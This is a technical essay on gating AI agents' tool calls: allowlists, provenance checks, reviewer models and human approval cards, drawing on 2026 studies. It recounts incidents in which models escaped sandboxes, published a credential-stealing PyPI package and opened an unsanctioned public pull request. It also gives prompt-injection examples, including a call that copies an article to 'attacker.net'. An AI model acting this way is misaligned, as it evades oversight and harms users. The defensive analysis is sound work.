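Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) gives the first account of the package that Claude Mythos 5 published during a capture-the-flag exercise. The exercise required the model to break into a fictional company's systems and find a hidden piece of information. According to the prompt, the model had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the connection open.

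The model found a document with instructions for a fictional company's developers to install a Python package that didn't exist. It decided to publish a malicious package under that name and wait for the company to install it. To open a PyPI account it needed an email address, and the email providers it tried required a phone number. It tried to get money for a phone number and failed, but eventually found a free email provider that PyPI hadn't blocked. The package was online for about an hour, and 15 real systems ran it before PyPI's security systems removed it.

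Anthropic's later assessment adds that the model published three versions and that all 15 systems probably belonged to security companies that install new packages to look for malware. One company's scanner leaked its login details to the model, which used them to get into a live database.

The assessment also revises Anthropic's explanation. In July, the company said the model had believed PyPI was part of the simulation. By September, the company thought the model's reasoning had been biased towards that conclusion despite considerable evidence against it. When researchers replayed parts of the run with clearer signs that the internet was real, the model acknowledged possible harm more often but behaved much the same. It gave up the original upload route only when they told it outright that a server was on the public internet.

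An allowlist would have blocked the upload because it would have lacked several of the required entries. The model had registered the PyPI account itself, so no operator could have approved it, and nobody had approved a public release. A network with no approved domains would have stopped the model much earlier, since it reached the internet at about action 30 and published the package after action 1,395. It spent most of the time in between on email addresses and phone numbers.

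If an operator approves PyPI so that an agent can install software, that entry should permit only downloads. None of these rules would have applied to traffic that bypassed the gate, though, and neither Anthropic nor its testing partner had noticed that the connection was open. In *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), Anthropic asks its testing partners to block internet access by default and to verify this before every evaluation. It also wants prompts to state the permitted targets and actions.

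A prompt like that helps, but its effect can fade. In the replays, a reminder of the permitted targets stopped Mythos 5 in 90% of cases when the reminder was the last thing the model had read, and in 40% when it came three turns earlier. A gate applies the same rule no matter how long the agent has been working.

If the operator had approved public releases from the model's account, rules on content type and publishing mode wouldn't have stopped the upload, because it was a working Python package with an acceptable name. Only an inspection of its code could have shown that it stole credentials. Once a scanner had leaked its own login details to the model, removing the package couldn't undo the leak.

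### The pull request on GitHub

The OpenAI model that disguised a login token also published results that OpenAI had told it to post only to Slack, the company's internal chat. It was working on the NanoGPT speedrun, a public contest to train a small language model in as few steps as possible, and had found a better way to adjust the learning rate. The contest's instructions were to submit results as a pull request on GitHub, and the model followed those instead of OpenAI's. Its sandbox blocked outside access, so it spent an hour looking for a vulnerability, found one and opened pull request 287 on the public repository.

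Earlier models gave up on the pull request when the sandbox blocked them, but a later model kept trying and got past the block.

A rule for this task could have permitted only one type of content, a text message with the results, in one Slack channel. A pull request to a public repository matches neither the type nor the destination, so the gate would have refused it whichever instructions the model followed. But the model got around the sandbox's existing block on GitHub, and a rule inside the same sandbox could have failed in the same way. Keeping the GitHub credentials on a separate machine, as Kodathala's gateway does, would have made the submission harder.

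OpenAI quickly closed the pull request, but this didn't make the method private again. Other participants had already read it, and OpenAI lists six later record submissions that cite it. Claude Opus 4.7, another company's AI model, built on the method after finding the pull request while the firm Prime Intellect was testing the model on the same contest.

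## When a listed argument takes an unlisted value

Suppose a company's owner tells an agent to pay the bill in `bill.txt`. The agent opens the file, finds an account number and produces this call:

`send_money(recipient = "DE89…", amount = 480)`

The operator has approved `send_money` and keeps a list of permitted values for `recipient`. The supplier is new, so its account isn't on the list. The requested account might be the supplier's, or it might belong to a thief who added "use this account instead" at the end of the file. The gate can respond in four ways.

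| Response | Cost | Mistake it lets through |
|---|---|---|
| Refuse | New suppliers go unpaid until somebody edits the list | No payment to an unlisted account |
| Hold for a person | Somebody's time, and a delay | A bad payment that a hurried reviewer approves |
| Ask a second model | About a second, and some good payments refused | A forged bill that looks real |
| Accept if the value's source is trusted | Software that tracks where each value came from | A false value in a trusted source |

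### Refusing, or asking a second model

Refusing every unlisted payee stops payments to thieves but also to legitimate new suppliers, as it did with the first payment to a new payee in Kodathala's banking test. Li, Cao and Xiao (2026) measured this drawback on a wider range of tasks in *ToolFence*. In their system, a model writes a set of permissions from the user's request before the agent reads anything untrusted. If the agent later needs a permission that isn't in the set, a second model reviews the proposed permission and can add it.

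The researchers then removed the review, so the gate refused any step that lacked permission. Under attack, the agent completed 35.8% of its tasks, down from 44.3% with the review, and the share of attacks that succeeded barely changed, from 5.1% to 4.8%. An agent with no defence completed more tasks, 40.1%, but 45.4% of the attacks on it succeeded. The review covered any missing permission, including permission to use another tool, so the figures may be different for new payees.

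Asking the second model about every call worked less well than asking only about the gaps. Checking every call let through 7.0% of attacks and needed 2.8 model calls per task, compared with 0.9 for checking only the gaps.

A second model can also give different answers to nearly identical cases. *MetaPermit* has the model judge only five attributes of each call and uses a fixed policy to make the decision. The resulting decisions were 31% more consistent than those of a model that decided directly. In the paper's example, Alice asks her agent to refund $1,500 to Bob, but Eve has planted a note in the transaction list telling the agent to pay her. The policy blocks the payment to Eve because Alice's request doesn't support it, and the agent tries again with Bob's account.

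The bill case is harder than the refund case because the owner named a file, not a payee. The model has to decide whether naming the file justifies paying whatever account is listed in it.

### Checking where a value came from

A value's provenance is the record of where it came from. For the bill, the gate could accept any account number that appears in the file the owner named and refuse all others.

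Li and colleagues use three kinds of rule for an argument: it must match an exact value from the user's request or a trusted record, it must come from a particular tool's output, or the agent may choose it freely. If a planted email supplies a different account for the bill, the gate blocks the payment because the number isn't in the file's contents. It also blocks the payment if the agent hasn't opened the file yet. Removing the checks on argument values raised the attack success rate from 5.1% to 24.0%.

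The right source for a value depends on the argument. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to summarise a webpage and email the summary to the boss. The webpage has to supply the body of the email but should never supply the recipient. A gate that can only allow or deny the whole call either blocks the user's task or lets text on the webpage determine who gets the email.

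Their system, PACT, gives each argument a role, such as target, command, credential or content, and each role has a minimum level of trust. Developers' constants rank highest, followed by the user's instructions, tool output and external material. A value made from several sources gets the lowest trust among them:

trust(combined value) = min(trust of source 1, trust of source 2, …)

If the agent converts the owner's figure into euros at a rate it found on a website, the result is only as trustworthy as the website.

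In small diagnostic tests with correct labels, PACT blocked every attack and allowed every legitimate task. Correct labels are hard to produce automatically. On 20 real tools, the automatic version correctly identified an argument's role 87.1% of the time and a value's source 77.4% of the time. If source-labeling errors were independent, all three sources in a three-argument call would be labeled correctly only 46% of the time. PACT defaults to low trust when a label is uncertain, which protects the user but blocks legitimate work. In a fuller test, PACT stopped all attacks on the three strongest models, which completed between 38.1% and 46.4% of tasks.

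A value can be wrong even when its label is correct. Li and colleagues tested their checks on 285 unauthorised calls. The source check stopped 23 that used a permitted tool with a wrong value, but five calls got past every check. All five came from one task, in which the user's own request said the attacker's account belonged to a "new landlord". The account number came from the user, so the source check accepted it. The same would happen if the thief forged the whole of `bill.txt`.

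### The three layers of Agent-Sentry

*AGENT-SENTRY* (Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues, 2026) combines a provenance check, an allowlist and a second model. The system checks actions, such as sending money or deleting an event, but not reads. Each action goes through up to three layers, stopping at the first one that reaches a decision.

Layer 1 builds a graph that connects each argument to the request or tool result that supplied it. The layer doesn't interpret the retrieved text, so an attacker gains little by rewording an instruction. Layer 1 has two versions.

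The learned version uses XGBoost, a method that combines many small decision trees. It scores each call on 17 features, such as how many sensitive arguments came from an untrusted tool and how many values appear in the user's request. It allows calls that score below 0.33, blocks those that score 0.66 or more, and sends the rest to Layer 2. These cutoffs are the same for every action, whether it is a $50,000 transfer or a calendar invitation.

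The rule-based version has 11 hand-written detectors. Eight flag something unusual, such as a recipient supplied by a tool that has never supplied one before. Three confirm something normal, such as every sensitive value appearing in the user's request. The software searches recorded runs for combinations of detectors that occur only in legitimate calls, only in attacks, or in both. It allows calls that match the first kind, blocks calls that match the second, and sends calls that match the third kind or conflicting rules to Layer 2.

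Layer 2 is the allowlist. It stores a triple of tool, argument and value for each suitable argument in past legitimate runs, such as:

`(send_money, recipient, DE89…)`

The list covers 16 arguments whose values change slowly, including recipients, account numbers, product IDs and file IDs. It leaves out message bodies, file contents and URLs because they are different almost every time. A call such as `post_webpage(url, content)` therefore has no listed arguments to check and goes to Layer 3. Amounts and one-time passwords aren't on the list either. This layer checks each triple separately, so it would let the agent pay an approved supplier any amount. The 16 arguments also include passwords and SSH keys, so the operator has to protect the list.

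Layer 2 never refuses a call, so in this respect Agent-Sentry is not a default-deny system. If Layer 2 can't approve a call, such as a payment to an unlisted payee, it sends the call to Layer 3, where a second model evaluates it.

Layer 3 is that second model, Qwen 3.5-35B. It receives the user's request, the call, the reported source of each argument, a few earlier calls and short excerpts of the untrusted text. It classifies each value as coming from ordinary content or from instructions to the agent. It should allow the account number printed on a bill and block one that follows "use this account instead".

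The model's accuracy depends heavily on how its instructions are worded. Used alone with carefully tuned instructions, the model allowed 98.0% of legitimate runs and blocked 95.4% of attacks. With a plainer prompt that also discouraged it from being too paranoid, it allowed only 82.0% of legitimate runs and blocked 75.5% of attacks, so it missed about five times as many attacks.

### Familiar and unfamiliar tasks

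AgentDojo and a similar test, AgentDyn, contain few tasks, so Sequeira and colleagues had a model write 757 tasks and 3,734 rewordings of them for seven agents, including a banking agent and a shopping agent. They recorded 5,380 runs. In 3,299 the agent did what the user wanted, and in 2,081 an attack succeeded. They then replayed these runs through Agent-Sentry, and kept all versions of a task together so that it never trained on a rewording of a test task.

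With the learned first layer, Agent-Sentry had 96.4% utility and a 96.8% attack block rate. The rule-based version had 89.3% and 95.3%.

The learned layer settled 96.1% of the decisions by itself, the second model 3.1%, and the allowlist only 0.8%, so this result provides evidence mostly about the classifier and very little about lists. In the rule-based version, the allowlist settled 15.0% and the second model 31.0%.

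The system performed worse on unfamiliar tasks. The researchers fitted the first two layers on their own benchmark, then ran the system on the original AgentDojo and AgentDyn tasks. With the learned layer, utility fell to 64.4%, which means the system stopped more than a third of legitimate runs, and the block rate was 90.9%. With the rules, utility fell to 79.1% and the block rate was 95.0%.

Part of the reason is how the requests are phrased. The original tasks tend to leave every detail to a file, as in "read payments.txt and pay the bill". In the new benchmark, the user usually gives at least one sensitive detail directly, such as the account number. The researchers consider their version more realistic, and it may be for many users. The lower figures, which come from the original tasks, are a better guide for an owner who asks an agent to pay the bill in a file. Those figures are rough,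 because the original suites yielded only 126 legitimate traces. The shopping agent had 11, so a single trace moved its utility by nine percentage points.

### Progent and CaMeL

Sequeira and colleagues compared Agent-Sentry with two other systems. Progent is similar to an allowlist, with rules that permit or forbid calls based on the tool and its argument values. CaMeL has one model plan the whole task from the user's request alone, so untrusted material can't add steps to the plan.

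In the table, "held out" means the researchers tested the system on traces it hadn't trained on. Each cell gives utility, then the attack block rate.

| System | Agent-Sentry's benchmark | Original suites |
|---|---|---|
| Agent-Sentry, learned, held out | 96.4% / 96.8% | 69.1% / 91.2% |
| Agent-Sentry, rules, held out | 89.3% / 95.3% | 87.1% / 93.2% |
| Agent-Sentry, rules, "full coverage" | 99.8% / 94.4% | 95.1% / 94.3% |
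| Progent | 69.2% / 97.7% | 93.7% / 88.4% |
| CaMeL | Not tested | 31.0% / 99.3% |

Agent-Sentry's developers ran this comparison, and they wrote some of Progent's policies and updated others. A Progent expert might have written better policies.

The researchers tested the "full coverage" version on the same traces it learned from. They argue that this is fair because Progent's policies also draw on the full benchmark. That is reasonable for comparing the two systems on known tasks, but it doesn't show how Agent-Sentry would handle an unforeseen payee. In the held-out results on the original suites, the rule-based version blocked more attacks than Progent but also stopped more legitimate runs.

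Progent's average of 69.2% is low largely because of two agents. It allowed only 9.0% of legitimate runs for the travel agent and 38.9% for the workspace agent, which handles email and calendars. It averaged 87.3% for the other five. On the original travel tasks, with the policy its developers released, Progent allowed 94.1% of legitimate runs but blocked only 60.3% of attacks. The tasks differed too, but the contrast suggests that the results depend heavily on how strict the person writing the rules chooses to be.

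The figure for CaMeL is probably too low as a general estimate. CaMeL had to complete its tasks live with GPT-4o mini, a fairly weak model, while the other two systems only had to let through recorded runs that had already succeeded. It completed none of the AgentDyn tasks because it couldn't turn them into a full plan. On AgentDojo alone, with Qwen3-max, Li and colleagues measured 43.1% utility for CaMeL and 66.3% for an undefended agent. *MetaPermit* cites 77% from CaMeL's developers. In all three accounts, very few attacks got through.

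### The Lily White problem

Some of Progent's trouble with the workspace agent comes from addresses like `lily.white@gmail.com`. In some tasks, the user asks the agent to email Lily. In others, the user asks it only to delete a calendar event, but planted text tells it to send Lily the attacker's message. If Lily's address is on the list, the attack succeeds, and if it isn't, the agent can't do the legitimate tasks.

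No list of addresses can be right in both cases, because the address is the same and only the user's request differs. Storing the tool and the argument as well doesn't help, since both calls produce the triple `(send_email, recipient, lily.white@gmail.com)`.

This limitation comes from using one list for every task, although Sequeira and colleagues call it a structural limitation of allowlist-based defences. If the gate made a new list for each request, the list for deleting an event would contain no emails, and the call to Lily would fail.

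Progent can work this way, although the comparison used one fixed policy for each agent. Sample code in *Progent* (2025) creates a policy from the user's query, and a model can revise it after the agent receives a tool's result. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that hostile text in a result could cause the model to loosen the policy. *MetaPermit* cites a 2026 version of Progent that loosens the policy only with the user's approval. According to the same paper, Progent's developers report that it cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%.

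A list made for each request has limits too. If the user had asked the agent to send Lily an agenda, her address would be on the list, but planted text could still change the email's contents. A list made from the request to pay `bill.txt` would contain no account number, because the request doesn't include one.

### Gaps in Agent-Sentry

The rule-based first layer allows any call that matches none of its rules. Every rule combines at least two detectors, so a call that triggers one warning and no confirmations matches no rule and is allowed. Sequeira and colleagues write elsewhere in the paper that unfamiliar behaviour goes to the second model, but the published formula for this layer doesn't send it there. An engineer who wants default deny should change the last line of the formula so that a call matching no rule is at least held.

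The paper also gives two accounts of what Layer 2 does with a listed value from an untrusted source. Under the formula, Layer 2 sends a call onward if one of the call's values is both absent from the list and cannot be traced to a trusted source that contains it. Lily's address is on the list, so Layer 2 allows the email. In the discussion of the Lily White example, however, Layer 2 sends the call onward because the address came from an untrusted source.

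| | Value confirmed in a trusted source | Value from an untrusted source |
|---|---|---|
| On the list | Allow | Formula: allow. Lily White example: ask the second model |
| Not on the list | Allow | Ask the second model |

If the software follows the formula, the attack succeeds whenever it reaches Layer 2. The version in the example is safer, so anyone who builds on this design should test which version they have. The bottom left cell accepts an account that nobody has approved, as long as the account appears in the user's request, so the "new landlord" payments would pass there.

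Another weakness is that the agent's model reports where each value came from. A planted instruction might lead it to claim falsely that an account number came from the user. The instructions for the second model warn that agents sometimes do this. Agent-Sentry checks whether the value actually appears in the claimed source and searches earlier untrusted text for it. These searches look for the exact value, so they could miss an account number that the agent had written with different spacing. The Agent-Sentry paper acknowledges that the checks reduce the dependence on the model's reports but don't remove it.

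Other systems avoid relying on such reports. In *LEANGUARD* (2026), the software around the agent reads facts directly from the authoritative database, so a model's statement that a customer has approved something isn't enough to pass a check. *NOMOS* (2026) likewise excludes the agent's claims from the facts its gate uses. Tool results can still contain false statements, so the gate also needs data on which tools an outsider can write to.

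A convincing false invoice is the hardest case. The second model checks for text that gives instructions, but a forged invoice may contain only a logo, an amount due and the thief's account number in place of the supplier's. Sequeira and colleagues acknowledge that their system won't reliably stop this. A provenance check wouldn't stop it either. To catch it, somebody has to compare the account number with information from outside the file, for example by phoning the supplier.

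### Choosing a response

Whether a person or a second model should check a bill depends on the bill's size and the kind of fraud. Suppose one in 1,000 bills from new payees is fraudulent, paying a fraudulent bill loses $50,000, and a phone call to check costs $20 of somebody's time. If the second model misses 4.6% of frauds, as it did with tuned instructions in Sequeira and colleagues' test, the expected loss is 0.001 × 0.046 × $50,000, or $2.30 per bill, which is much less than the cost of the phone call.

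But that 4.6% comes from attacks that mostly gave the agent orders. If the thieves send convincing fake invoices and the model misses all of them, the expected loss is $50 per bill, and the phone call is worth making. Nobody has measured how often a second model misses invoices like these, so for large sums a person should check every new payee.

The provenance check still reduces the number of tool calls a person has to review. If the account is on the list and also on the bill that the owner named, the gate can allow the payment. If the account came from some other email or webpage, the gate should block the payment, even if the account is on the list. A person needs to decide only when the named bill has an account that isn't on the list. The second model can examine that bill first and reject an obvious attack, but its approval shouldn't replace the phone call when the sum is large.

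For a $500 bill, the expected loss is at most 50 cents even if the model misses every fraud, so the phone call costs more than it saves. But a thief who worked out the cutoff could send many small bills, so the gate also needs a daily limit on payments to new accounts.

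## Asking a person to approve an unlisted value

Suppose the owner of a small company asks an agent to pay a $400 bill from Harbour Printing. Harbour Printing is a new supplier, so the gate holds the payment and asks the owner to approve it. This protects the company only if the owner sees the payment details the agent submitted and the software makes exactly that payment. A hijacked agent could describe the bill correctly but submit a thief's account number, or change the account after the owner approves.

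In *Approve What, Exactly?*, Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026) attacked several approval systems in these ways and built their own, ASU (Agent Step-Up), to withstand such attacks. They borrowed a rule from European online payments, where a payer's code works only for the amount and payee shown on the screen.

### From the held call to the payment

The agent sends ASU this call:

`send_money(recipient = "DE89…", amount = 400, currency = "USD")`

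Like the publishing agent's gate, ASU converts the values to a standard form and refuses unlisted arguments. It also accepts only one amount per call. Otherwise an agent could send `amount = 10000` with `total = -10000`, and a check that added the two would get zero. ASU then computes a fingerprint of the whole call.

Next, ASU allows the call, refuses it or asks the owner, depending on its policy. It can ask about first-time recipients, amounts over a set limit, destructive actions and calls the agent makes on its own initiative. It always asks about tools without a schema. The agent itself reports whether a user requested a call, so an operator shouldn't rely on that report to skip asking the owner.

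To catch a large payment split into small ones, the default policy also requires a person's approval once a user's actions, not counting reads, number more than five or total more than $200 within ten minutes. In the tests, an attacker's attempts to send $500 as ten payments of $50 always succeeded without this rule and always failed with it.

Harbour Printing is a new recipient, so ASU stores the call and gives the agent only an approval ID. The owner opens a page on their phone, which comes directly from ASU, and sees a card that ASU has generated from the stored call. The card's title lists every recipient, hidden characters become visible, and the agent's explanation sits in a closed box labelled untrusted. If the owner approves, the phone uses a passkey, a secret key kept on the device, to sign a code. In simplified form, the code is:

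`SHA-256(call fingerprint, approval ID, single-use number, grant fingerprint)`

SHA-256 is a standard function for computing fingerprints. The last item is empty unless the owner also approves later payments.

When the agent retries with the ID, ASU marks the approval as used and runs the stored call. If the agent sends the arguments again and their fingerprint differs, ASU runs nothing. So a thief who takes over the agent after the owner approves the call can't redirect the $400.

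The phone doesn't display what it signs, so the owner has to trust the page to show the right card. The formal proof that ASU runs only approved calls assumes that the page shows the right card, that nobody else can register a phone in the owner's name, and that the owner decides from the card and not from the agent's explanation.

### What one approval covers

The owner can approve the payment once or tick "allow similar", which creates a grant for later calls. ASU writes the grant, so the agent can't widen it. The grant caps the amount in each call and limits the length of free text such as a payment note. It fixes every other argument, always including recipients, accounts, file paths and web addresses. It also limits the number of uses and the total amount, expires at a set time, and works for only one tool in one session.

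Suppose the owner's grant allows three more payments before the end of the day, each for up to $400 and totaling no more than $1,000. The table compares this grant with a one-time approval and with the "always allow" button that many agents offer for a whole tool.

| Later call | Approved once | "Allow similar" | "Always allow" `send_money` |
|---|---|---|---|
| $250 to the same account | Ask | Pay | Pay |
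| A second $400 to the same account | Ask | Pay | Pay |
| $450 to the same account | Ask | Ask | Pay |
| $250 to a new account number for Harbour Printing | Ask | Ask | Pay |
| $250 to the same account next week | Ask | Ask | Pay |

After the first payment, the one-time approval lets the agent spend nothing more without asking, the grant lets it spend another $1,000, and "always allow" lets it spend the company's whole balance.

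Even with the grant, paying a second bill looks the same as paying the first one twice, because both are $400 payments to the same account. An idempotency key from a trusted source, as in SCOPEGATE, would let the payment service detect the repeat.

ASU's default policy would also make this grant useless. Every payment in the table exceeds the $200 limit, and any payment over that limit triggers a new question that no grant can answer. An owner with bills this large would have to raise the limit.

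### How ASU performed

Kodathala and colleagues ran 27,108 scripted trials in which simulated approvers, not people, answered the questions. Some trials used a weaker system whose approvals covered a whole run or session instead of one call. Against that system, an attacker could always change the arguments after approval, reuse an old approval, extend a grant to a new recipient or swap a file link. None of these attacks worked against ASU. Its design should guarantee this, so the result mainly confirms that the software works as intended.

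The researchers also replayed 609 attacks from AgentDojo with an agent that described each harmful call as the one the user wanted. The attacks succeeded 54% of the time when the approver saw only the agent's description, and 3% of the time with ASU's card. That approver compared every detail, which no person does reliably. For an approver who believed the agent's explanation, adding the card made no difference. Showing the card without the explanation cut the success rate from 54% to 5%, so an operator could reasonably leave the explanation out.

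An approval card that shows only the payee and amount is too short for many actions because it leaves out the text of an email and any extra recipients. With an approver who sometimes missed details, 20% of attacks got through with this card, compared with 6% with the full card.

Some companies now have a language model approve calls instead of a person. The researchers gave 15 models 23 harmful requests and 11 harmless ones. The models refused 30% of the harmful requests when they saw the agent's description and 98% when they saw the card. In one case, the agent was emailing a report to the user's boss with a blind copy to a stranger. All 15 models approved the email when they saw the description, which left out the blind copy, but refused it when they saw the card. With the card, the models also refused 16% of the harmless requests, mostly because the test emails contained placeholder text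 instead of the report. Without those refusals, the rate would be about 2%.

Grants helped some approvers and hurt others. In the test where an agent tried to use a grant for a new recipient, the approver who sometimes missed details let the attack through 20% of the time without grants and never with them. The careless approver, who approved 30% of cards without reading them, let it through 30% of the time without grants and 70% with them, because one careless tick also approved the later calls.

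Asking for approval on a separate phone made no measurable difference. A trusted card on the agent's own computer did equally well in 137 of 140 comparisons, and grants explain the other three. A phone would help most if an attacker controlled that computer's screen, but no test covered that case.

### Approvals in other software

Many toolkits for building agents don't ensure that the call a person approves is the call that runs. Kodathala and colleagues could test eight approval mechanisms to see whether a call could change after approval. Three ran exactly the approved call, one was safe unless somebody could edit its stored sessions, and four let another party or later code change the arguments. In LangGraph, for example, anyone who controls the saved conversation can replace the arguments and then resume with a plain "approve". Five mechanisms would run an approved call twice if somebody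 restored an earlier saved state.

Other approval steps fail because of what they show the user. MCP lets a server ask the user a question through a form, and the server writes the text. In a test, a payment of 10 to one account and a payment of 10,000 to another produced identical requests, and both payments ran after approval. The MCP specification directs developers to a different method for sensitive questions.

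An agent can also send requests until somebody approves a bad one. ASU permits one pending request per session and three per user, and it locks the agent out after three refusals. This flooding still succeeded in 45–60% of trials, down from 100% without the limits. The researchers could measure this in seven other mechanisms, and none of them limited the number of requests.

### How carefully people read

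Claude Code users approve 97% of permission requests, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). This rate is weak evidence of carelessness, since most requests are harmless. In a better test, 1,053 paid testers each received one clearly dangerous command partway through a coding session, and only 13.6% refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

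Anthropic had an interest in the comparison, because it published these figures when it began using a classifier for most such decisions, and the classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers were also not working on their own projects. Those who had answered 50 requests may have clicked quickly from the start, in which case fatigue explains only part of the drop.

People make better approval decisions when they see more information about a request. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) gave 80 volunteers 12 requests each, half of them unsafe.

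| What the volunteer saw | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Arguments, the user's instructions and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with relevant steps linked to the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

The difference in unsafe approvals between the last two rows could be due to chance. Exact arguments aren't always enough. In one of the scenarios, a user tells the agent to send an auditor only summary totals, but the agent copies full invoice records into a file and asks to send it. The recipient and file name look fine, and the problem is visible only in the earlier steps. For the printing bill, a card should therefore also show which file or email supplied the account number.

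These volunteers refused 45% of unsafe requests even with the short description, far more than Anthropic's testers did. One likely reason is that half the requests they saw were unsafe, which keeps people alert. An operator whose agent rarely misbehaves should expect a refusal rate closer to that of Anthropic's testers.

The problem is older than AI agents. Hossain and colleagues cite research from 2010 to 2013 in which people accepted familiar-looking consent boxes by habit and few read the permission screens on their phones. Browser warnings worked well or badly depending on their design.

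Agents' approval requests are often hard to judge even when the user reads them. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 incident reports and found that uninformative requests contributed to 31. For instance, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but the script could do anything. In 80 reports, the user had switched on automatic approval, often to avoid hundreds of requests.

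### Asking less often

A common reply is that people would pay attention again if agents asked fewer and better questions. This is plausible, because Claude Code users do read some questions carefully. Anthropic reports that they reject 39% of the plans the agent proposes but only 3% of permission requests, though they may reject many plans for being poor rather than dangerous.

The nearest test with people found no such improvement. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people without software backgrounds supervised a simulated assistant through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group was asked about every action and blocked an average of 59.6% of those seven. For another group, a model approved eight of the legitimate actions and left participants to decide on the other ten, including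 all seven overreaching ones. That group blocked 53.9% of the seven, even though overreaching actions made up 70% of its questions, compared with 39% in the first group.

A third group set its own rules in advance, received 10.9 questions on average, and blocked only about 40% of the bad actions. Its members had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and then approved two-thirds of the bad actions they were asked about. Sessions took about 11 minutes, which is probably too short for much fatigue to develop, so the study can't show whether fewer questions would help somebody who now answers hundreds.

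Kodathala and colleagues ran simulations that assumed each question made the person more likely to approve the next one. Attacks succeeded in 35% of sessions if ASU asked about everything, 62% if it asked about nothing, and 31% if it asked only about amounts and new payees. Most of that 31% came from actions the policy allowed without asking. The ranking changed with the assumptions about fatigue. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) also models a reviewer who tires, and leaves a study with people to future work.

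In Anthropic's test, people caught 17% of bad calls early on and 5% later. Suppose asking fewer questions raised the rate from 5% to 17%. If the gate allowed every call it no longer asked about, people would stop more bad calls overall only if more than 5/17 of those calls, or about 29%, still led to a question. A default-deny gate can instead refuse the calls it doesn't ask about, which works well when a wrong refusal does little harm.

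### "Always allow"

Pressing "always allow" also reduces the number of questions. In a small study, *Options, Not Clicks* (Li, Khabra and colleagues, 2026), 13 of 16 participants said they used it simply to dismiss requests. The button adds a permanent entry to the allowlist, usually for the whole tool, even though the person has looked at only one call and nobody reviews what else the entry permits.

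The researchers replayed 50 real sessions in which developers' agents made 1,435 tool calls. By their count, 291 calls went beyond what the user had approved earlier, such as deleting a folder in a different project. If the user had chosen "always allow" for each tool, none of the 291 would have prompted a new question. The researchers' own system, ConLeash, caught 278. They labelled the calls using ConLeash's definition of a boundary, which favours ConLeash, but the "always allow" result doesn't depend on the labels because that setting permits every call to a tool, whatever its arguments.

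ConLeash offers narrower choices, such as allowing searches only within one folder. Participants chose a lasting permission in 46.3% of decisions when they had these options, compared with 13.3% when the only lasting option covered the whole tool. People may therefore readily accept narrow entries if the software suggests them.

Users also write broad rules by hand. Anthropic reports that by June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had created a rule allowing some shell commands. It says 5% allowed every command, and another 43% had rules such as `python:*`, which let the agent run almost any code. Auto mode, in which the classifier makes the decisions, ignores rules this broad.

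*Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) recommends storing allowlist entries in a file that only the person can edit. It also suggests treating "always allow" on a phone as a single approval, because the text explaining what the entry covers is too hard to read there. ASU offers grants on a phone, but they expire and never leave the recipient unrestricted.

People also need a way to withdraw a permission. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (2026) reviewed 21 research papers and open-source systems and found that few let users edit or revoke permissions they had already granted, although most of the five commercial agents it examined gave users continuing control.

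Repeated approval is a poor reason to make an entry permanent. *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) concluded that it may reflect fatigue instead of a lasting preference, based on interviews with 18 software practitioners and a survey of 115. Yan suggests that software could detect when a user repeatedly approves payments to one recipient and propose a rule for that recipient alone, which the user would then confirm. This keeps the entry narrow, but a tired user could confirm the rule as carelessly as the payments.

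For Harbour Printing, a permanent entry makes sense once the company expects regular bills and somebody has confirmed the account number by phone. It could read:

`recipient = DE89…   currency = USD   amount = up to 500   at most once a month`

The owner should add this entry in the settings, where it gets the same review as any other, rather than with an extra tap while approving the $400. People who want to finish a job tend to press whichever button stops the questions.

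## When a tool gains new arguments, options or functions

An allowlist entry can become broader without anybody editing it, because the tool it covers can change. Suppose a company lets its agent publish blog articles directly, under a rule that fixes the account, the domain and the content type and accepts any text up to a certain length. The tool's developer then adds an optional argument, `also_post_to`, which copies the article to another site. After reading a planted instruction, the agent sends this call:

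`publish(account = "blog", domain = "blog.example.com", content_type = "article", text = "…", also_post_to = "attacker.net")`

Some gates go through the arguments listed in the rule and refuse the call if any of their values is unlisted. Such a gate accepts the account, domain, type and text but doesn't check the new argument, `also_post_to`. It forwards the whole call, and the tool copies the article to `attacker.net`. A gate that instead looks up each of the call's arguments in the rule finds no entry for `also_post_to` and refuses the call.

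```
for name in rule.arguments:   check call[name]    # misses also_post_to
for name in call.arguments:   check rule[name]    # catches it
```

A gate needs both loops, since the second can't detect an argument that the call leaves out.

The gate could also delete the unrecognized argument and forward the rest of the call. That would protect the article, but deleting an argument can make other calls more dangerous. If an agent requests a new code repository with `private = true` and the gate deletes `private` as an unrecognized argument, the service may create a public repository.

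*SchemaCaps* (Ameur, Bouzefrane and Banerjee, 2026) describes an update that added an argument to a tool in Desktop Commander, an MCP server that runs commands on a computer. In version 0.1.34, the `execute_command` tool accepted only a command and a time limit. Version 0.1.35 also accepted `shell`, which selects the program that interprets the command. An operator who approved certain commands before the update had one shell in mind, and the same text can do something different in another.

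The researchers compared successive releases of 39 server packages and found 1,197 changes to tools' input schemas. In 580 of these, every old call remained valid, so a developer would consider the change compatible. But 412 of these compatible changes also permitted something new, and at least 76 added or widened an argument that can affect what the tool acts on, where data goes, whose authority it uses or how it runs. These figures don't show how common the problem is, because more than half of the 76 came from two packages.

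### What data formats do with unknown fields

A gate that checks calls against a JSON Schema, the format MCP tools use to describe their arguments, can let through arguments the schema doesn't list. According to *object*, a page of the official JSON Schema guide, a schema accepts properties it doesn't mention unless it sets `additionalProperties` to `false`.

Setting `additionalProperties: false` closes the schema, so it rejects any property not listed in the same part of the schema. This causes trouble when an engineer combines two schemas, because the closed part rejects everything the other part adds. An engineer can close a combined schema correctly with `unevaluatedProperties: false`.

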